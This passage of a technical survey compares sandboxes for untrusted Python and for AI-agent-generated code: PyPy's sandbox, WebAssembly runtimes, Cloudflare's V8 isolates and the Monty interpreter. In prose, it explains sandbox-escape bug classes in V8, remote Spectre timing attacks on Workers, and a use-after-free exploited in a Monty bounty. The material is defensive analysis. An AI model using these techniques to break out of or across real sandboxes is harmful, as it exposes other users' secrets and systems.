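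In 2019 Anvil, a British company that still relied on an old version of PyPy's sandbox, paid for a month of work to revive it. In *A second life for the Sandbox*, Rigo (2019) described the sandbox as suited to whole programs, "not small bits of code inside your larger Python program".

His new version imitates the boundary between a process and the kernel. To write to a file, the guest sends a file number, a memory address and a length, and the controller reads that part of the guest's memory. Rigo (2019) explains in *Sandbox 2* that the interpreter can now request any system call without special preparation, and that the controller's author chooses which ones to support. This makes the interpreter easier to maintain but leaves more of the security work to the controller. The new version had no memory or time limits of its own, so Rigo suggested using the operating system's.

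That October, PyPy (2019) announced that the revived sandbox would come out soon. In 2023 someone asked on the project's mailing list how to use it with Python 3. The reply in Sayyad (2023), *Using pypy sandboxing with Python 3.x*, quoted the documentation's warning that it describes an old, unmaintained version. The warning, which was still there in June 2026, links to two development branches, the newer one for Python 3.6, and adds that later versions of Python require a threading module that might help a guest escape.

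In a reply to mavdol (2026), *Sandboxing Untrusted Python*, a programmer describes a new use for Sandbox 2 in a tool that collects the operations an AI agent tries to perform and shows them to the user before carrying them out.

### How WebAssembly confines a program

PyPy's sandbox relies on how one toolchain generates C code. WebAssembly builds similar restrictions into the instruction format, so they apply to any program compiled to it, even one with as much old C code as CPython. A compiler translates the program into a WebAssembly module, which a runtime on the host computer usually translates into machine code.

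The module keeps its data in *linear memory*, an array of bytes numbered from zero. A pointer in the guest is a position in this array, and the runtime makes sure every access falls inside it. If the array has 100 million bytes and the guest tries to read byte 200 million, the runtime stops the guest. The signing key is outside the array, so no pointer in the guest can refer to it. In the common 32-bit version, the array can grow to at most 4 GiB.

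WebAssembly also limits which code can run next. Attackers often exploit a memory bug in a native program by overwriting a function's return address. WebAssembly keeps return addresses outside linear memory and has no instruction for jumping to an arbitrary address, so a program can enter a function only by calling it. When the program chooses which function to call at run time, the runtime checks that the function takes the expected types of arguments.

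WebAssembly also has no instruction for a system call. A module lists the functions it imports, and the host has to supply all of them before the module can start. A module without imports can only calculate. WASI, the WebAssembly System Interface, is a standard set of imports for things like files, clocks and random numbers, and it lets the host choose which directories the guest can access.

A bug in CPython can still let an attacker take over the interpreter, but to escape the sandbox the attacker also needs a mistake in the runtime or in a function the host supplies. For example, the guest may be able to escape if the runtime's compiler leaves out a single check on a memory access.

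### What CPython loses in WebAssembly

Python needs its interpreter inside the sandbox because functions such as `eval()` run new source code, as the programmer Simon Willison explains in *Running Python code in a sandbox with MicroPython and WASM*. Developers therefore compile CPython's C code to WebAssembly and give the compiled interpreter the Python script as data.

Pyodide is a version of CPython built this way, mainly for web browsers. Other projects build CPython for WASI, which suits servers better. The two kinds of build differ most in how they handle native extensions. Pyodide can load an extension such as Pandas, a library for working with tables, once somebody has compiled it to WebAssembly. WASI has no such dynamic linking, so developers have to build each extension into the interpreter's module in advance.

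The software company HubSpot did this for Boomslang, a library that runs sandboxed Python inside a Java program. HubSpot's *Architecture* page lists CPython 3.14 with NumPy, Pandas, matplotlib and several other extensions. Users can add pure-Python packages, but they have to rebuild the module to add another native package. A first build of the whole system takes about an hour.

In return, a malicious native extension can no longer read the signing key because, like everything else in the sandbox, it can access only the guest's linear memory.

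Standard WASI also lacks threads and direct network connections, according to Morph's *WebAssembly Sandbox*, an overview by a company in this market, though the Wasmer runtime offers an extended version with both. Python's usual libraries for web requests may not work, and developers then have to supply a substitute that sends requests through the host.

The code also runs more slowly. In *Isolation Without Taxation*, Kolosick, Narayan and colleagues (2021) found that Firefox took 1.1 seconds to render a page of text with a native font library written in C and 2.0 seconds with the WebAssembly version. They used a compiler from 2020 that didn't optimize code very well, and they cite an earlier study that found an average slowdown of about 45% on other programs. These figures are only a rough guide for CPython. In Boomslang, the choice of runtime can matter more. HubSpot translates the module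 into Java bytecode in advance, and without this step it runs roughly ten times slower.

### One host call in Boomslang

Boomslang also has a version for Python hosts. HubSpot's *Python Host (boomslang-py)* guide shows how a host makes one of its functions available. The receipt program could offer exchange rates like this:

```python
@sandbox.host_function("exchange_rate")
def exchange_rate(args):
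    return {"rate": RATES[args["currency"]]}
```

The parser inside the sandbox would then request a rate:

```python
import json
from boomslang_host import call

reply = call("exchange_rate", json.dumps({"currency": "EUR"}))
rate = json.loads(reply)["rate"]
```

First, `json.dumps` turns the guest's dictionary into a string in the guest's linear memory. The guest also sets aside a buffer of up to 1 MiB for the answer. It then calls an imported WebAssembly function with six integers: the positions and lengths of the function's name, the JSON text, and the buffer. HubSpot's *Extension ABI JSON & Lowering* specifies this format.

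The host now copies the name and the JSON text out of the guest's memory and looks for a function registered under that name. If there isn't one, the guest gets a Python error. Otherwise the host turns the JSON into a dictionary of its own, runs `exchange_rate` and turns the result into JSON. It writes this text into the guest's buffer and returns the length of the text. In the guest, `json.loads` then creates a new dictionary.

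The host can't trust any of the six integers. A hostile guest might send values that place the start of its text near the end of linear memory and the end of the text far beyond it. HubSpot's Java version stops a guest that sends such values, and the Rust version returns an error.

A result may also be too large for the buffer. In the basic format, the host then returns −2, which the guest turns into a Python exception. The Python version of Boomslang avoids this by fetching a larger result in several pieces, so the guest's programmer doesn't have to do anything. HubSpot's format for asynchronous calls, which lets a guest wait for several host functions at once, doesn't yet split results and encodes them as base64 text, so a single result has to be smaller than about 768 KiB.

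To call `parse`, the host reserves some of the guest's memory, copies the argument there and starts the function. The argument has to be valid text, so the receipt program would need to encode a binary upload as text or put it in a directory that the guest can read.

### Objects that can't cross

Boomslang's format lets only strings, integers, floating-point numbers and bytes cross the interface. HubSpot's *Calling Host Functions from Python* recommends JSON for anything more complicated. Lists and dictionaries of simple values then arrive as copies, and changing a copy doesn't affect the original. A tuple arrives as a list. Python's standard JSON encoder rejects dates and sets, so a programmer has to convert those first.

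An open file can't pass between host and guest, because its file number doesn't refer to that file on the other side. A function can't either, although the host can register one under a name. An object loses its methods when it crosses, which keeps `sign` from accidentally running the guest's code.

Large tables are the hardest case. A Pandas table with a million rows and ten columns of numbers takes up about 80 MB. If each number needs 20 characters in JSON, the text takes up 200 MB, and Boomslang has to fetch it in about 190 pieces. The guest then has to create ten million Python numbers before it can build its own table. For a while, the guest's memory holds the text, the numbers and the interpreter at the same time.

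A host could avoid the text by saving the table as a binary file in the guest's `/work` directory, where Pandas can load it directly. null program's *WebAssembly as a Python extension platform* (2026) describes a more direct method for guests that expect plain numbers at a known position. The Python host reserves some linear memory and writes the numbers into it, which is faster in one operation for the whole list than in a loop. NumPy can also treat part of the guest's memory as an array. Writing directly to memory works well for a small compiled function, but a Python object also has a type, a reference count and pointers to other objects, which the guest's interpreter has to create itself.

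### When a crossing can be an ordinary function call

Kolosick and colleagues studied what a crossing between host and guest still involves when the only arguments are a few numbers. Host and guest take turns on the same processor core, so they use the same registers. Suppose Firefox keeps the address of an image in a register while it calls the font library. By convention, a function that uses this register must restore its old value before returning. A library controlled by an attacker could leave a different address there, and Firefox might then overwrite its own memory at a location the attacker chose. Registers can also contain secrets left over from the host's earlier work.

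Most runtimes prevent this with extra code around each call. This code saves the host's registers, clears any that might contain secrets and switches to a separate stack, then undoes all of this when the call ends. An optimized version took 120 nanoseconds per call, compared with 1 nanosecond for an ordinary C function call.

The team proved that a runtime can safely leave out this extra code if every function in the guest follows these rules:

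- It restores the registers that the convention tells it to preserve.
- It jumps only to places within itself, and returns only to its caller.
- It calls other functions only at their beginning and with the arguments they expect.
- It uses only its own part of the stack.
- It reads a register or local variable only after writing to it.

WebAssembly requires enough structure to guarantee all of this, as long as the compiler translates the module correctly. To avoid relying on the compiler, Kolosick and colleagues wrote VeriZero, which checks the finished machine code. For example, it rejects code if a function reads a register that might still contain one of the host's secrets. VeriZero took 2 to 19 seconds to check each of 13 compiled files, and it found all nine bugs the team had planted. The host has to run this check only once, before it first uses the code.

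Without the extra code, a call took 7 nanoseconds. The team attributes the remaining difference from C to the WebAssembly compiler, which optimized less. Rendering text in Firefox took 2.03 seconds instead of 2.25, which was enough of an improvement for Mozilla to release the sandboxed font library to its users.

However, this result measures only the transfer of control, and marshalling takes additional time. For 10,000 calls, going from 120 to 7 nanoseconds saves about 1.1 milliseconds. If writing and reading the JSON took 5 microseconds per call, it would add 50 milliseconds, which faster crossings wouldn't reduce. Faster crossings help most when a program makes many short calls that pass a few numbers, as Firefox does with fonts. For a Python host that exchanges dictionaries with its guest, making fewer calls is the better first step.

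### A sandbox for an agent or for each of its tasks

*An AI agent sandbox for agents that write and run code*, from the cloud company Akamai, describes an agent that runs in a WebAssembly sandbox. The code it writes runs in a restricted JavaScript or Python runtime inside that sandbox. This code has no network access by default, and neither the agent nor its code can raise the execution limits. In the technical preview, an agent works for about a minute, then stops until its next instruction.

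The outer boundary protects Akamai and its other customers, while the inner one is supposed to keep generated code away from the agent's data, such as its access keys. The inner boundary is weaker if the inner runtime shares the agent's linear memory, because a memory bug in the inner interpreter could then expose those keys. The attacker would still be inside the outer sandbox.

A programmer who goes by mavdol argues for smaller sandboxes, with one for each task an agent performs, because different tasks need different permissions. In mavdol's project, *Capsule*, a programmer puts a decorator above a Python function, much as in Threadbox:

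```python
@task(name="parse", ram="256MB", timeout="10s",
      allowed_hosts=[])
def parse(upload: str) -> list:
    ...
```

Capsule gives each task its own interpreter, although it looks like a sandbox around one function. It uses componentize-py to package the code with CPython, and runs every task in a separate WebAssembly sandbox. In the discussion *Show HN*, mavdol confirms that each JavaScript sandbox has its own engine. The same follows for Python, because an interpreter's heap and modules are in linear memory, and each execution gets its own memory, according to Glama's *Capsule server* page. Tasks can share the compiled code because it doesn't change.

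The task therefore receives copies of its arguments and returns its result as JSON. If it changes a global variable, the change doesn't affect other tasks. Capsule supports only pure Python in its sandboxes, so a task can't use NumPy or Pandas.

The decorator can make it hard to see what is inside the sandbox. Willison commented in the discussion that he would find Capsule easier to trust if the sandboxed code were in a separate file. A separate file would also be safer for the receipt program. Capsule compiles the programmer's file into the module, so a signing key written in the same file as `parse` could end up in the sandbox.

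By default, a Capsule task can't read the host's files or environment variables, but it can contact any website, which is why the example sets `allowed_hosts` to an empty list. Capsule also sets no default limit on memory or running time.

HubSpot warns in its guide to an earlier Java version of Boomslang that a timeout can't interrupt Python code that never calls a host function. Such code keeps running on one of only ten threads, so ten malicious uploads could block the service. HubSpot suggested adding a process boundary for such code. The Python version uses a different runtime, Wasmtime, which does stop the guest at the timeout.

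### Start-up time and memory

Starting CPython and importing NumPy and Pandas takes seconds in WebAssembly. HubSpot does this once, when it builds Boomslang, and saves the resulting linear memory in the module. Each new interpreter then starts from this snapshot, with the libraries already loaded. Cloudflare also uses snapshots for customers who run Python on its servers, but it takes them when a customer uploads a program. Briefly's *Python Workers Redux* summarizes Cloudflare's results.

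The projects report the following times:

| System | Start-up time |
|---|---|
| Boomslang in Java | Milliseconds for each new interpreter |
| Boomslang in Python | Up to minutes the first time on a machine, then under a second for each new process |
| Cloudflare, with large packages | About 1 second, down from nearly 10 |
| Capsule | Seconds from source code, milliseconds once compiled |

These figures show that most of the delay comes from compiling the module and initializing Python, both of which a host can do before the first upload arrives. They measure different things, so they don't show which system is fastest.

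Memory is harder to save, because each sandbox in the Python version of Boomslang has a full copy of the snapshot. A sandbox needs at least 150 MB, even to parse a tiny file, and typically uses several hundred. HubSpot recommends resetting a sandbox to its original state and reusing it instead of creating more. As with Hyperlight, the reset also prevents one customer's data from reaching the next customer.

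The Java version uses copy-on-write instead. All interpreters read from one snapshot of several hundred megabytes, and each gets a private copy of a 64 KiB page only when it writes to that page. In CPython, even reading an object can trigger a copy because it changes the reference count stored in the object's page, but a short script touches only a small part of NumPy and Pandas. A host can therefore give every upload a fresh interpreter with all its libraries, as long as most of the snapshot stays unchanged.

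## Many JavaScript engine instances in one process: V8 isolates

A sandboxed Python interpreter with its usual libraries takes up at least 150 MB in Boomslang, which limits how many a machine can run. Cloudflare, which runs programs for websites on servers around the world, fits thousands of customers onto each machine. It gives each customer's program its own instance of a JavaScript engine and puts many instances in one process. Each instance then needs only a few megabytes, but a bug in the engine can expose one customer's data to another.

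### What an isolate contains

V8 runs JavaScript and WebAssembly in Google's Chrome browser. An *isolate* is one instance of V8 with its own heap and global variables, much like an interpreter instance in Python. All isolates in a process share one copy of V8's machine code, which helps keep each isolate small.

JavaScript code can't turn a number into a pointer, and the language itself has no functions for opening files or network connections. A guest gets such functions only if the host supplies them. If `parse` were a JavaScript function in its own isolate, the references it could follow would lead only to objects in that isolate and whatever the host had given it.

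V8 enforces the separation between isolates in software. The isolates' heaps share one address space, and the processor normally lets any code in a process read all of that process's memory.

### Why Cloudflare doesn't give each customer a process

Cloudflare's customers upload programs called Workers, which run in hundreds of locations to be close to their users. Some locations have room for only a few machines, but every customer's program has to be available there. According to Cloudflare's *Security model*, each machine therefore has to host thousands of active customers, each using at most a couple of megabytes.

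*Cloud Computing without Containers* (Bloom, 2018) compared isolates with Amazon's Lambda, which started a process in a container for each copy of a program. An isolate started in 5 milliseconds and used about 3 MB, while a Lambda process took between half a second and 10 seconds to start and used 35 MB even if the program did nothing.

Switching between processes also takes up to 100 microseconds, by Bloom's figures. Many Workers need less than a millisecond for each request, so one processor core may switch between thousands of customers every second. At 100 microseconds each, 5,000 switches would use half of the core's time. Cloudflare estimates that giving every customer a process could easily increase processor use tenfold.

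The 5-millisecond figure no longer applies to large Workers. Cloudflare's *Eliminating Cold Starts 2* (2025) explains that the company has since allowed bigger programs, which take longer to fetch, compile and initialize. Cloudflare now sends requests for rarely used Workers to a machine that already has the program running. Forwarding a request this way adds less than a millisecond, and it reduced the share of large customers' requests that wait for a Worker to start from 0.1% to 0.01%.

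A drawback of reusing an isolate is that its global variables survive from one request to the next. Cloudflare's *How Workers works* advises customers not to store mutable data in them. The isolate separates Cloudflare's customers from each other, but not the users of a single customer's program.

### When V8 has a bug

V8 compiles frequently used JavaScript to machine code while the program runs, and its compilers leave out checks that seem unnecessary. *The V8 Sandbox* (2024) gives a simplified example of what can go wrong. A function converts each element of an array to a number. The conversion can run code supplied by the guest, which can shorten the array. If the compiler assumed that the length couldn't change, the function may then write past the end of the array and damage another object.

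Rewriting V8 in a memory-safe language such as Rust wouldn't solve this problem, because a compiler written in Rust can still produce faulty machine code. About half of the V8 bugs that attackers exploited were in its compilers. Of the Chrome exploits found in real attacks between 2021 and 2023, 60% started in V8.

Cloudflare limits the damage from such bugs with an outer sandbox around the whole process. The sandbox uses seccomp and Linux namespaces, which give a process its own view of resources such as the file system. Cloudflare loads the V8 runtime first and then blocks all file access before any customer's code arrives. A container usually can't be this strict, because it has to read the guest program from disk.

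The process can't use the network either. It can only contact other programs on the same machine, which carry out requests for it. One fetches a Worker's code, but only if the process presents the encryption key for that Worker. Another checks outgoing web requests and blocks those addressed to Cloudflare's internal services.

The outer sandbox protects the machine and customers in other processes, but not customers who share a process with the attacker. Cloudflare therefore groups customers by how much it trusts them. For example, a customer on the free plan never shares a process with a large corporate customer. Cloudflare also installs V8 fixes within 24 hours of publication, since attackers can study a published fix to find the bug.

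### Confining damage to the heap

V8's developers have added another barrier inside the process, the *heap sandbox*. They assume that attackers will sometimes corrupt JavaScript objects, and the sandbox is meant to keep the damage from spreading to the rest of the process.

In Chrome, V8 reserves one terabyte of address space for these objects and removes all ordinary pointers from it. An object refers to another by its distance from the start of the region, stored as a 40-bit number, which can't express a location outside the region. To refer to something outside, an object stores a position in a protected table, where V8 looks up the real address. This design resembles WebAssembly's linear memory and slows typical programs by about 1% or less.

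But V8's trusted code still has to read lengths, positions and types from objects that an attacker may have changed. If it uses a false length without checking it, it may write past the end of a buffer outside the region.

*Empirical Security Analysis of Software-based Fault Isolation through Controlled Fault Injection* (Bars, Schloegel and Bernhard, 2025) presents SbxBrk, a tool built to find such mistakes. It adds a check before each instruction in V8 that might read from the region. While V8 runs a JavaScript test file, the tool flips some bits in a value just before V8 reads it. The changed value stays in memory, so later reads return it too. If the change causes V8 to run code that earlier tests hadn't reached, the tool saves the change and tries further ones. A memory checker reports any resulting damage outside the region.

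The team compared SbxBrk with a modified version of Fuzzilli, Google's tool for testing JavaScript engines. In ten three-day runs, SbxBrk found six bugs and Fuzzilli found one of those six. In total, SbxBrk found 19 bugs that could let an attacker out of the heap sandbox:

- Four were *double fetches*, where V8 reads a value twice and assumes that it hasn't changed. For example, V8 might use one reading of an array's length to create a buffer and another to decide how much of the buffer to sort.
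- Four involved a value that should be one of a fixed set of options. V8 had no instructions for any other value, so its behavior became unpredictable.
- Two were *use-after-free* bugs, where V8 keeps using memory that it has already released.
- The other nine were mostly buffer overflows and similar writes to the wrong place, often because a very large length caused a calculation to overflow.

Google fixed 17 of them and marked the other two as duplicates.

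To use any of these bugs, an attacker would first need a different bug that corrupts the heap. The double fetches usually also require a second thread to change the value at the right moment. Cloudflare doesn't allow Workers to use threads, so they should be harder to exploit there than in a browser. Sandlock's supervisor had to be written to avoid the same kind of mistake when checking network addresses.

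V8's developers hoped in 2024 that escapes from the heap sandbox would come from simple mistakes, such as missing length checks, which standard tools can prevent. Many of the 19 bugs fit that description, but whether a bug exists can also depend on how a compiler translates V8's own source code. One bug appeared only when V8 was compiled without optimization, because the optimized version kept a value in a register instead of reading it again. Bars and colleagues compared two versions of the compiler released about six months apart and found that the number of reads differed for 2.8% of the relevant lines of code. Developers therefore can't check the source once and assume it will stay safe.

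The study's 19 bugs aren't a full count of the ways one Cloudflare Workers customer might get at another's data. According to V8's README for the heap sandbox, only writes outside the region count as violations, because the developers assume that an attacker can already read memory outside it. This is reasonable in Chrome, which puts different websites in different processes, but in Workers the same process holds other customers' secrets. Bars and colleagues found several out-of-bounds reads but didn't report them because Google usually doesn't fix such bugs.

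### Thousands of heap sandboxes in one process

Cloudflare couldn't use the heap sandbox as it was, because V8 put all the isolates in a process into the same sandbox. The isolates' heaps would have had to share 4 GiB, and a corrupted object in one could have damaged the others. Corry and Gupta describe in *Safe in the sandbox* how Cloudflare paid the software company Igalia to change V8 so that each isolate could have its own sandbox.

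Each of Cloudflare's heap sandboxes reserves 8 GiB of address space, though it uses far less actual memory. A Linux process normally has 128 TiB of address space, enough for at most 16,384 sandboxes. V8 usually leaves 32 GiB empty around a heap sandbox, because a corrupted array could reach that far beyond the edge. With one 32 GiB gap between neighboring sandboxes, only about 3,300 would fit.

Cloudflare instead uses memory protection keys, the processor feature that Enclosures uses to switch between memory views. V8 needs some keys for its compilers, which leaves about 12. Cloudflare assigns these in rotation, so no two heap sandboxes within 32 GiB of each other have the same key. The processor then blocks a corrupted array from accessing a neighboring sandbox's memory, so the sandboxes don't need empty space between them.

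With thousands of isolates and 12 keys, many isolates must share a key. If an attacker could read from any address, the keys would stop only about 11 of every 12 attempts to read another randomly chosen isolate. The rotation gives full protection only as long as the heap sandbox keeps the attacker within 32 GiB. As in Enclosures, an attacker who can run arbitrary machine code can change which keys are active.

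### Reading another customer's memory through timing

Even if V8 has no bugs, Spectre attacks can leak data between isolates through the processor. To save time, a processor guesses the result of a check and continues before it knows the answer. If the guess was wrong, it discards the results, but some of the data it read may remain in its cache, a small, fast memory. Reading cached data takes slightly less time, so a program that can measure the difference may be able to work out a secret it was never allowed to read.

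Spectre can also affect separate processes and virtual machines, but operating systems and hypervisors have defenses at those boundaries. Isolates in the same process have no such boundary between them. Chrome's developers stopped trying to prevent Spectre within a process and moved each website into its own process.

Cloudflare tried to make the attack too slow to be useful. The clock that a Worker can read doesn't advance while its code runs, and Workers can't use threads to build their own. Cloudflare also restarts the runtime every day, which moves everything to new places in memory. It watches for unusual activity in the processor and moves suspicious Workers to their own processes. *Dynamic Process Isolation* (2021), which introduced this last measure, rejected memory protection keys because 16 keys seemed too few for thousands of Workers.

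A Worker can still contact an outside computer that has a working clock. At first, Cloudflare couldn't build a remote attack that worked on its real servers, even with help from Spectre experts. In 2021, researchers used an outside clock to read 120 bits per hour, but only tested this on a local network. In *Remote-Timer-as-a-Service* (2026), Schwarzl, Xiao and colleagues worked with Cloudflare to make such an attack work on the real servers. They read a login token from a victim Worker they had set up, at up to 12 bits per second with 99% accuracy. At that rate, an attacker who had already found a 256-bit signing key in memory could read it in about 21 seconds, compared with over two hours at the 2021 rate.

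In *A revisit of remote Spectre attacks on Cloudflare Workers*, Schwarzl and Pedersen give two reasons why Cloudflare's detector missed the attack. The detector moved a suspicious Worker only after its current run ended, and a run could last for hours. It also measured suspicious events relative to the Worker's other activity, so heavy network traffic made the attack look normal.

Cloudflare found no sign that anyone had used the attack against customers. Before Schwarzl and colleagues published it, the company improved the detector and introduced the heap sandbox and the protection keys. The researchers confirmed that the heap sandbox stops their version of the attack, but they expect other versions may still work. They conclude that software measures alone weren't enough and that the hardware has to enforce the separation.

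Another option is to keep secrets out of the process. LeakLess, a research system that Schwarzl and colleagues discuss, stores secrets elsewhere and adds them to a Worker's requests on the way out. Developers have to mark each secret by hand, and the system can't help when the Worker itself needs to process private data. It works better for access keys, which a program often only has to pass on.

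### Code Mode and Dynamic Workers

Cloudflare also uses isolates to run code that language models write. In *Code Mode* (September 2025), Varda and Pai proposed that an AI agent should write a short program that calls its tools, as Microsoft's agents later did with Hyperlight. Each program runs in a new isolate, which Cloudflare discards afterwards, so every run gets a fresh domain, whereas an ordinary Worker serves many requests in the same one.

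Cloudflare made the underlying feature, Dynamic Workers, available to all paying customers as a test version in March 2026. A JavaScript version of the receipt program could use it like this:

```js
const worker = env.LOADER.load({
  compatibilityDate: "2026-03-01",
  mainModule: "parse.js",
  modules: { "parse.js": untrustedCode },
  env: { RATES: ratesService },   // the only way out
  globalOutbound: null            // no internet access
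});
const orders = await worker.getEntrypoint().parse(upload);
```

`RATES` is a *binding*, an object whose methods send requests to the host. The guest might call `env.RATES.lookup("EUR")`, and the host would look up the rate and return it. If the host needs an access key for the exchange-rate service, it adds the key on its own side, so the guest never has the key and can't leak it.

Developers can also filter the guest's web requests. Varda, Pai and Gupta, in *Sandboxing AI agents, 100x faster*, recommend bindings instead, because a filter has to interpret every detail of a request to determine whether it's safe. With a binding, the developer writes only the functions the guest should have. But a guest that can read private messages through one binding and post publicly through another can leak the messages without any access key or general network access.

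According to Varda and colleagues, a Dynamic Worker starts in a few milliseconds, about 100 times faster than a typical container, and uses a few megabytes of memory. It usually runs on the same thread as the Worker that created it, so a crossing between the two doesn't have to go over the network. The planned price is $0.002 per day for each different program, or $2 for a thousand one-off scripts, plus the usual charge for processor time.

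However, running on the same thread also puts the guest in the same process as the host. The receipt program would be safer if it kept its signing key in a separate service, so that the guest couldn't get the key through a bug in V8 or a timing attack. Blocking the guest's internet access should make timing attacks harder, because the guest can't contact an outside clock directly, but it could still use a binding that reveals the time.

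Varda and colleagues acknowledge that security bugs are more common in V8 than in typical hypervisors, which is why Cloudflare surrounds isolates with many other defenses. A company that just ran V8 in its own server would get the small, fast instances without most of this protection.

Isolates also can't run ordinary Linux programs. For agents that need to install packages or run shell commands, Cloudflare offers *Sandboxes*, a separate service that uses containers.

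### Why Python's subinterpreters are different

Python's *subinterpreters*, separate interpreter instances that can run in one process, look much like isolates. *Multiple Interpreters in the Stdlib* (Snow, 2017) described them as running in "relative isolation" from one another, but Snow wanted them mainly for concurrency. Since Python 3.12, each subinterpreter can have its own lock for running Python code, so several can run at the same time on different processor cores.

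The two designs differ most in what the guest can do from the start:

| | Isolate in Cloudflare Workers | Python subinterpreter |
|---|---|---|
| Files and network | Only through functions that the host supplies | Whatever the process may use |
| Machine code from the guest | Not accepted | Native extensions can access the whole process |
| Memory corruption | Heap sandbox and protection keys limit it | Can affect every interpreter in the process |

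A guest in a subinterpreter therefore doesn't need to find a bug to reach the host's files or memory.

A host that tried to block file access and extensions from inside Python would face the same problem as pysandbox. Even if the host succeeded, an attacker could still look for a memory bug in CPython's C code, and CPython has nothing like V8's heap sandbox to contain the damage.

Cloudflare runs its customers' Python code with Pyodide rather than relying on subinterpreters, so CPython runs as WebAssembly inside an isolate (*Python Workers redux*). The guest can use most of Python, and V8 enforces the boundary around the whole interpreter.

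## Interpreters written for untrusted code: Monty and CaMeL

Pyodide can run most Python programs because it is CPython, and V8 has to contain everything that CPython might do. The pysandbox project tried instead to remove abilities from CPython, but people kept finding ones it had missed. A third approach is to write a new, much smaller interpreter that can't open files, use the network or import anything from outside unless the host provides a way to do so.

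Monty and CaMeL are recent interpreters with different purposes. Monty runs programs that a language model wrote and nobody reviewed. CaMeL runs programs that the host mostly trusts but that handle untrusted data, and it records where each value came from. The host can use these records to let a program email one address but not another.

### A smaller Python

Monty comes from Pydantic, the company behind a popular Python library for checking data. According to Pydantic's *monty 0.0.21*, the interpreter is written in Rust, a memory-safe language, and contains no part of CPython. It translates a script into its own simple instructions and executes those. The script can't call native code.

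Pydantic's *Security Model* stresses that Monty has no code for dangerous operations, rather than code that blocks them. Without the host's help, a guest can't read a file or an environment variable, open a connection or start a process. It can read the clock and get random numbers, but the host can replace both.

The tradeoff is that Monty supports only part of Python. Pydantic's *Limitations* lists functions, simple classes, comprehensions, pattern matching and `async` among the supported features. Monty rejects generator functions, `del` and properties before it runs anything, and a script can't define its own exception types. Monty includes 32 standard library modules, most of them incomplete. Pydantic left out `socket`, `subprocess` and `ctypes` on purpose, while others just haven't been added yet. Third-party packages, including NumPy and Pandas, don't work.

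In the receipt program, Monty could probably run a new parser for a text format such as CSV. A parser for a binary format would be harder, because Python programmers usually read binary data with the `struct` module, which Monty lacks. A contractor's existing script would often need rewriting.

A language model can do that rewriting itself if it gets a clear error message. In *pydantic-monty investigation*, Willison (2026) had an AI agent review Monty and reports that unsupported features generally fail cleanly. Differences that raise no error are more dangerous. For example, Monty ignores a class's `__bool__` method, so an object that should count as false counts as true, and the script continues with the wrong answer.

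Coverage is growing quickly. Documentation from spring 2026 listed only five modules. But each new module adds code that the host has to trust.

### Pausing at a host call

A Monty guest reaches the host through *external functions*, which the host names and implements. When the guest calls one, Monty stops the whole program and returns control to the host:

```python
from pydantic_monty import Monty

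with Monty() as pool:
    with pool.checkout() as session:
        paused = session.feed_start('12 * exchange_rate("EUR")')
        # paused.function_name is "exchange_rate"
        # paused.args is ("EUR",)
        done = paused.resume({"return_value": 1.5})
        print(done.output)        # 18.0
```

The guest's code doesn't define `exchange_rate`, so Monty pauses there and gives the host the function's name and arguments. The host can look up the rate by any method. `resume` then puts 1.5 in place of the call, and the guest continues with the multiplication. File operations work the same way, because the interpreter never accesses a disk. It pauses with a description of the operation, and the host's code determines what happens next.

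If the host doesn't need this much control, it can supply a dictionary of functions, and Monty's library answers the calls automatically.

PyPy's sandbox also makes the guest wait for the host, but the guest occupies a live process while it waits. Monty can turn the paused program into bytes with `dump()` and continue it later in a different process or on another machine. If an agent's program tries to make a payment, the host could pause at that call, store the bytes in a database and ask a person, who might answer the next day. The person can approve each call after seeing its actual arguments, whereas in Microsoft's system for running generated programs in Hyperlight, a person approves the whole program before it starts.

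The host has to protect these saved programs. Mintlify's *Sandbox Isolation*, documentation for an early version of Monty, warns that a snapshot from an untrusted source could bypass the resource limits or execute arbitrary code. A host therefore shouldn't let customers store their own snapshots and send them back.

Monty can also give a guest limited access to a live object, which Boomslang's JSON interface can't. The host wraps the object and lists the attributes the guest may read and the methods it may call. Everything else stays hidden by default, and each permitted method runs in the host. If a method returns another object, such as the customer's session, the host has to wrap that one too. When the guest passes the host an instance of a class defined in guest code, the host receives a read-only stand-in.

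### What Monty leaves to the host

Pydantic promises only that a guest can't reach anything the host didn't supply. Host functions run with all of the host's permissions, so they have to check their arguments.

The host also has to set limits on memory, running time and the number of host calls. The running-time clock stops while the guest waits for the host, so a slow database doesn't use up the guest's time. Monty checks the time only at certain points in the program, and a guest might get stuck between them. Pydantic therefore advises setting a separate deadline, after which the host kills the guest's process. There is no such deadline by default when Monty runs on the host's own machine. After a guest hits a memory or time limit, the host should discard the session because Monty's internal records may be damaged.

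Pydantic (2026) released version 1.7.0 in November and marks it as stable. It runs every Python session in a separate worker process, so a crash in a session can't crash the host. The workers start without the host's environment variables and have never loaded the signing key.

But like PyPy's subprocess, a worker has no seccomp filter or container around it, so an attacker who took over the worker could make ordinary system calls. A host could add a process sandbox such as Sandlock.

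The host also reuses each worker, by default for up to 1,000 sessions. A compromised worker could read later users' data, so Pydantic recommends a new worker for each session if the users don't trust each other. The library can also connect to workers on other machines, where the guarantees depend entirely on what those machines run, which may be ordinary CPython with no sandbox.

### A break-in within two days

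In April 2026, Pydantic offered $5,000 to anyone who could read a secret from a server that ran strangers' code in Monty. According to *Hack Monty* (Hewitt, 2026), the server received almost 1.5 million requests from about 650 addresses. Someone read the secret in less than 48 hours.

Rust normally prevents a program from using memory that it has already released. For speed, Monty's developers had switched off some of these checks in a few small sections of code, which Rust requires programmers to mark as `unsafe`. That code was correct only if Monty's garbage collector never removed an object that was still in use. A bug in the collector caused it to do so, and an attacker used the bug to run arbitrary code. Hewitt thinks the same bug would almost certainly have caused only crashes or wrong results without the `unsafe` code.

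Pydantic fixed the bug in version 0.0.16 and rechecked the other `unsafe` sections. Hewitt takes it as a good sign that more than a million attempts turned up only one hole of this kind. This is some evidence of safety, but the number of attempts is a poor measure of effort, since one skilled person needed less than two days to find it. CPython's C code has far more places where a similar mistake could occur, but it has had decades of use, while Monty is new.

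In *Hack Monty 2* (Colvin, 2026), the software company Prefect explains why it helped pay for a second round with a $10,000 prize. Prefect runs Monty inside its own software, where an escape from the sandbox compromises the host directly. Pydantic's *Hack Monty* describes a third round in August, run on a server that gives each visitor a separate worker process, again with no second sandbox behind Monty.

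The move to worker processes also makes Monty's best-known figures harder to use. The early documentation compares start-up times as follows:

| Method | Start-up time |
|---|---|
| Monty | 0.06 ms |
| `exec` in the host's own CPython | 0.1 ms |
| New Python process | 30 ms |
| Docker | 195 ms |
| Pyodide | 2,800 ms |

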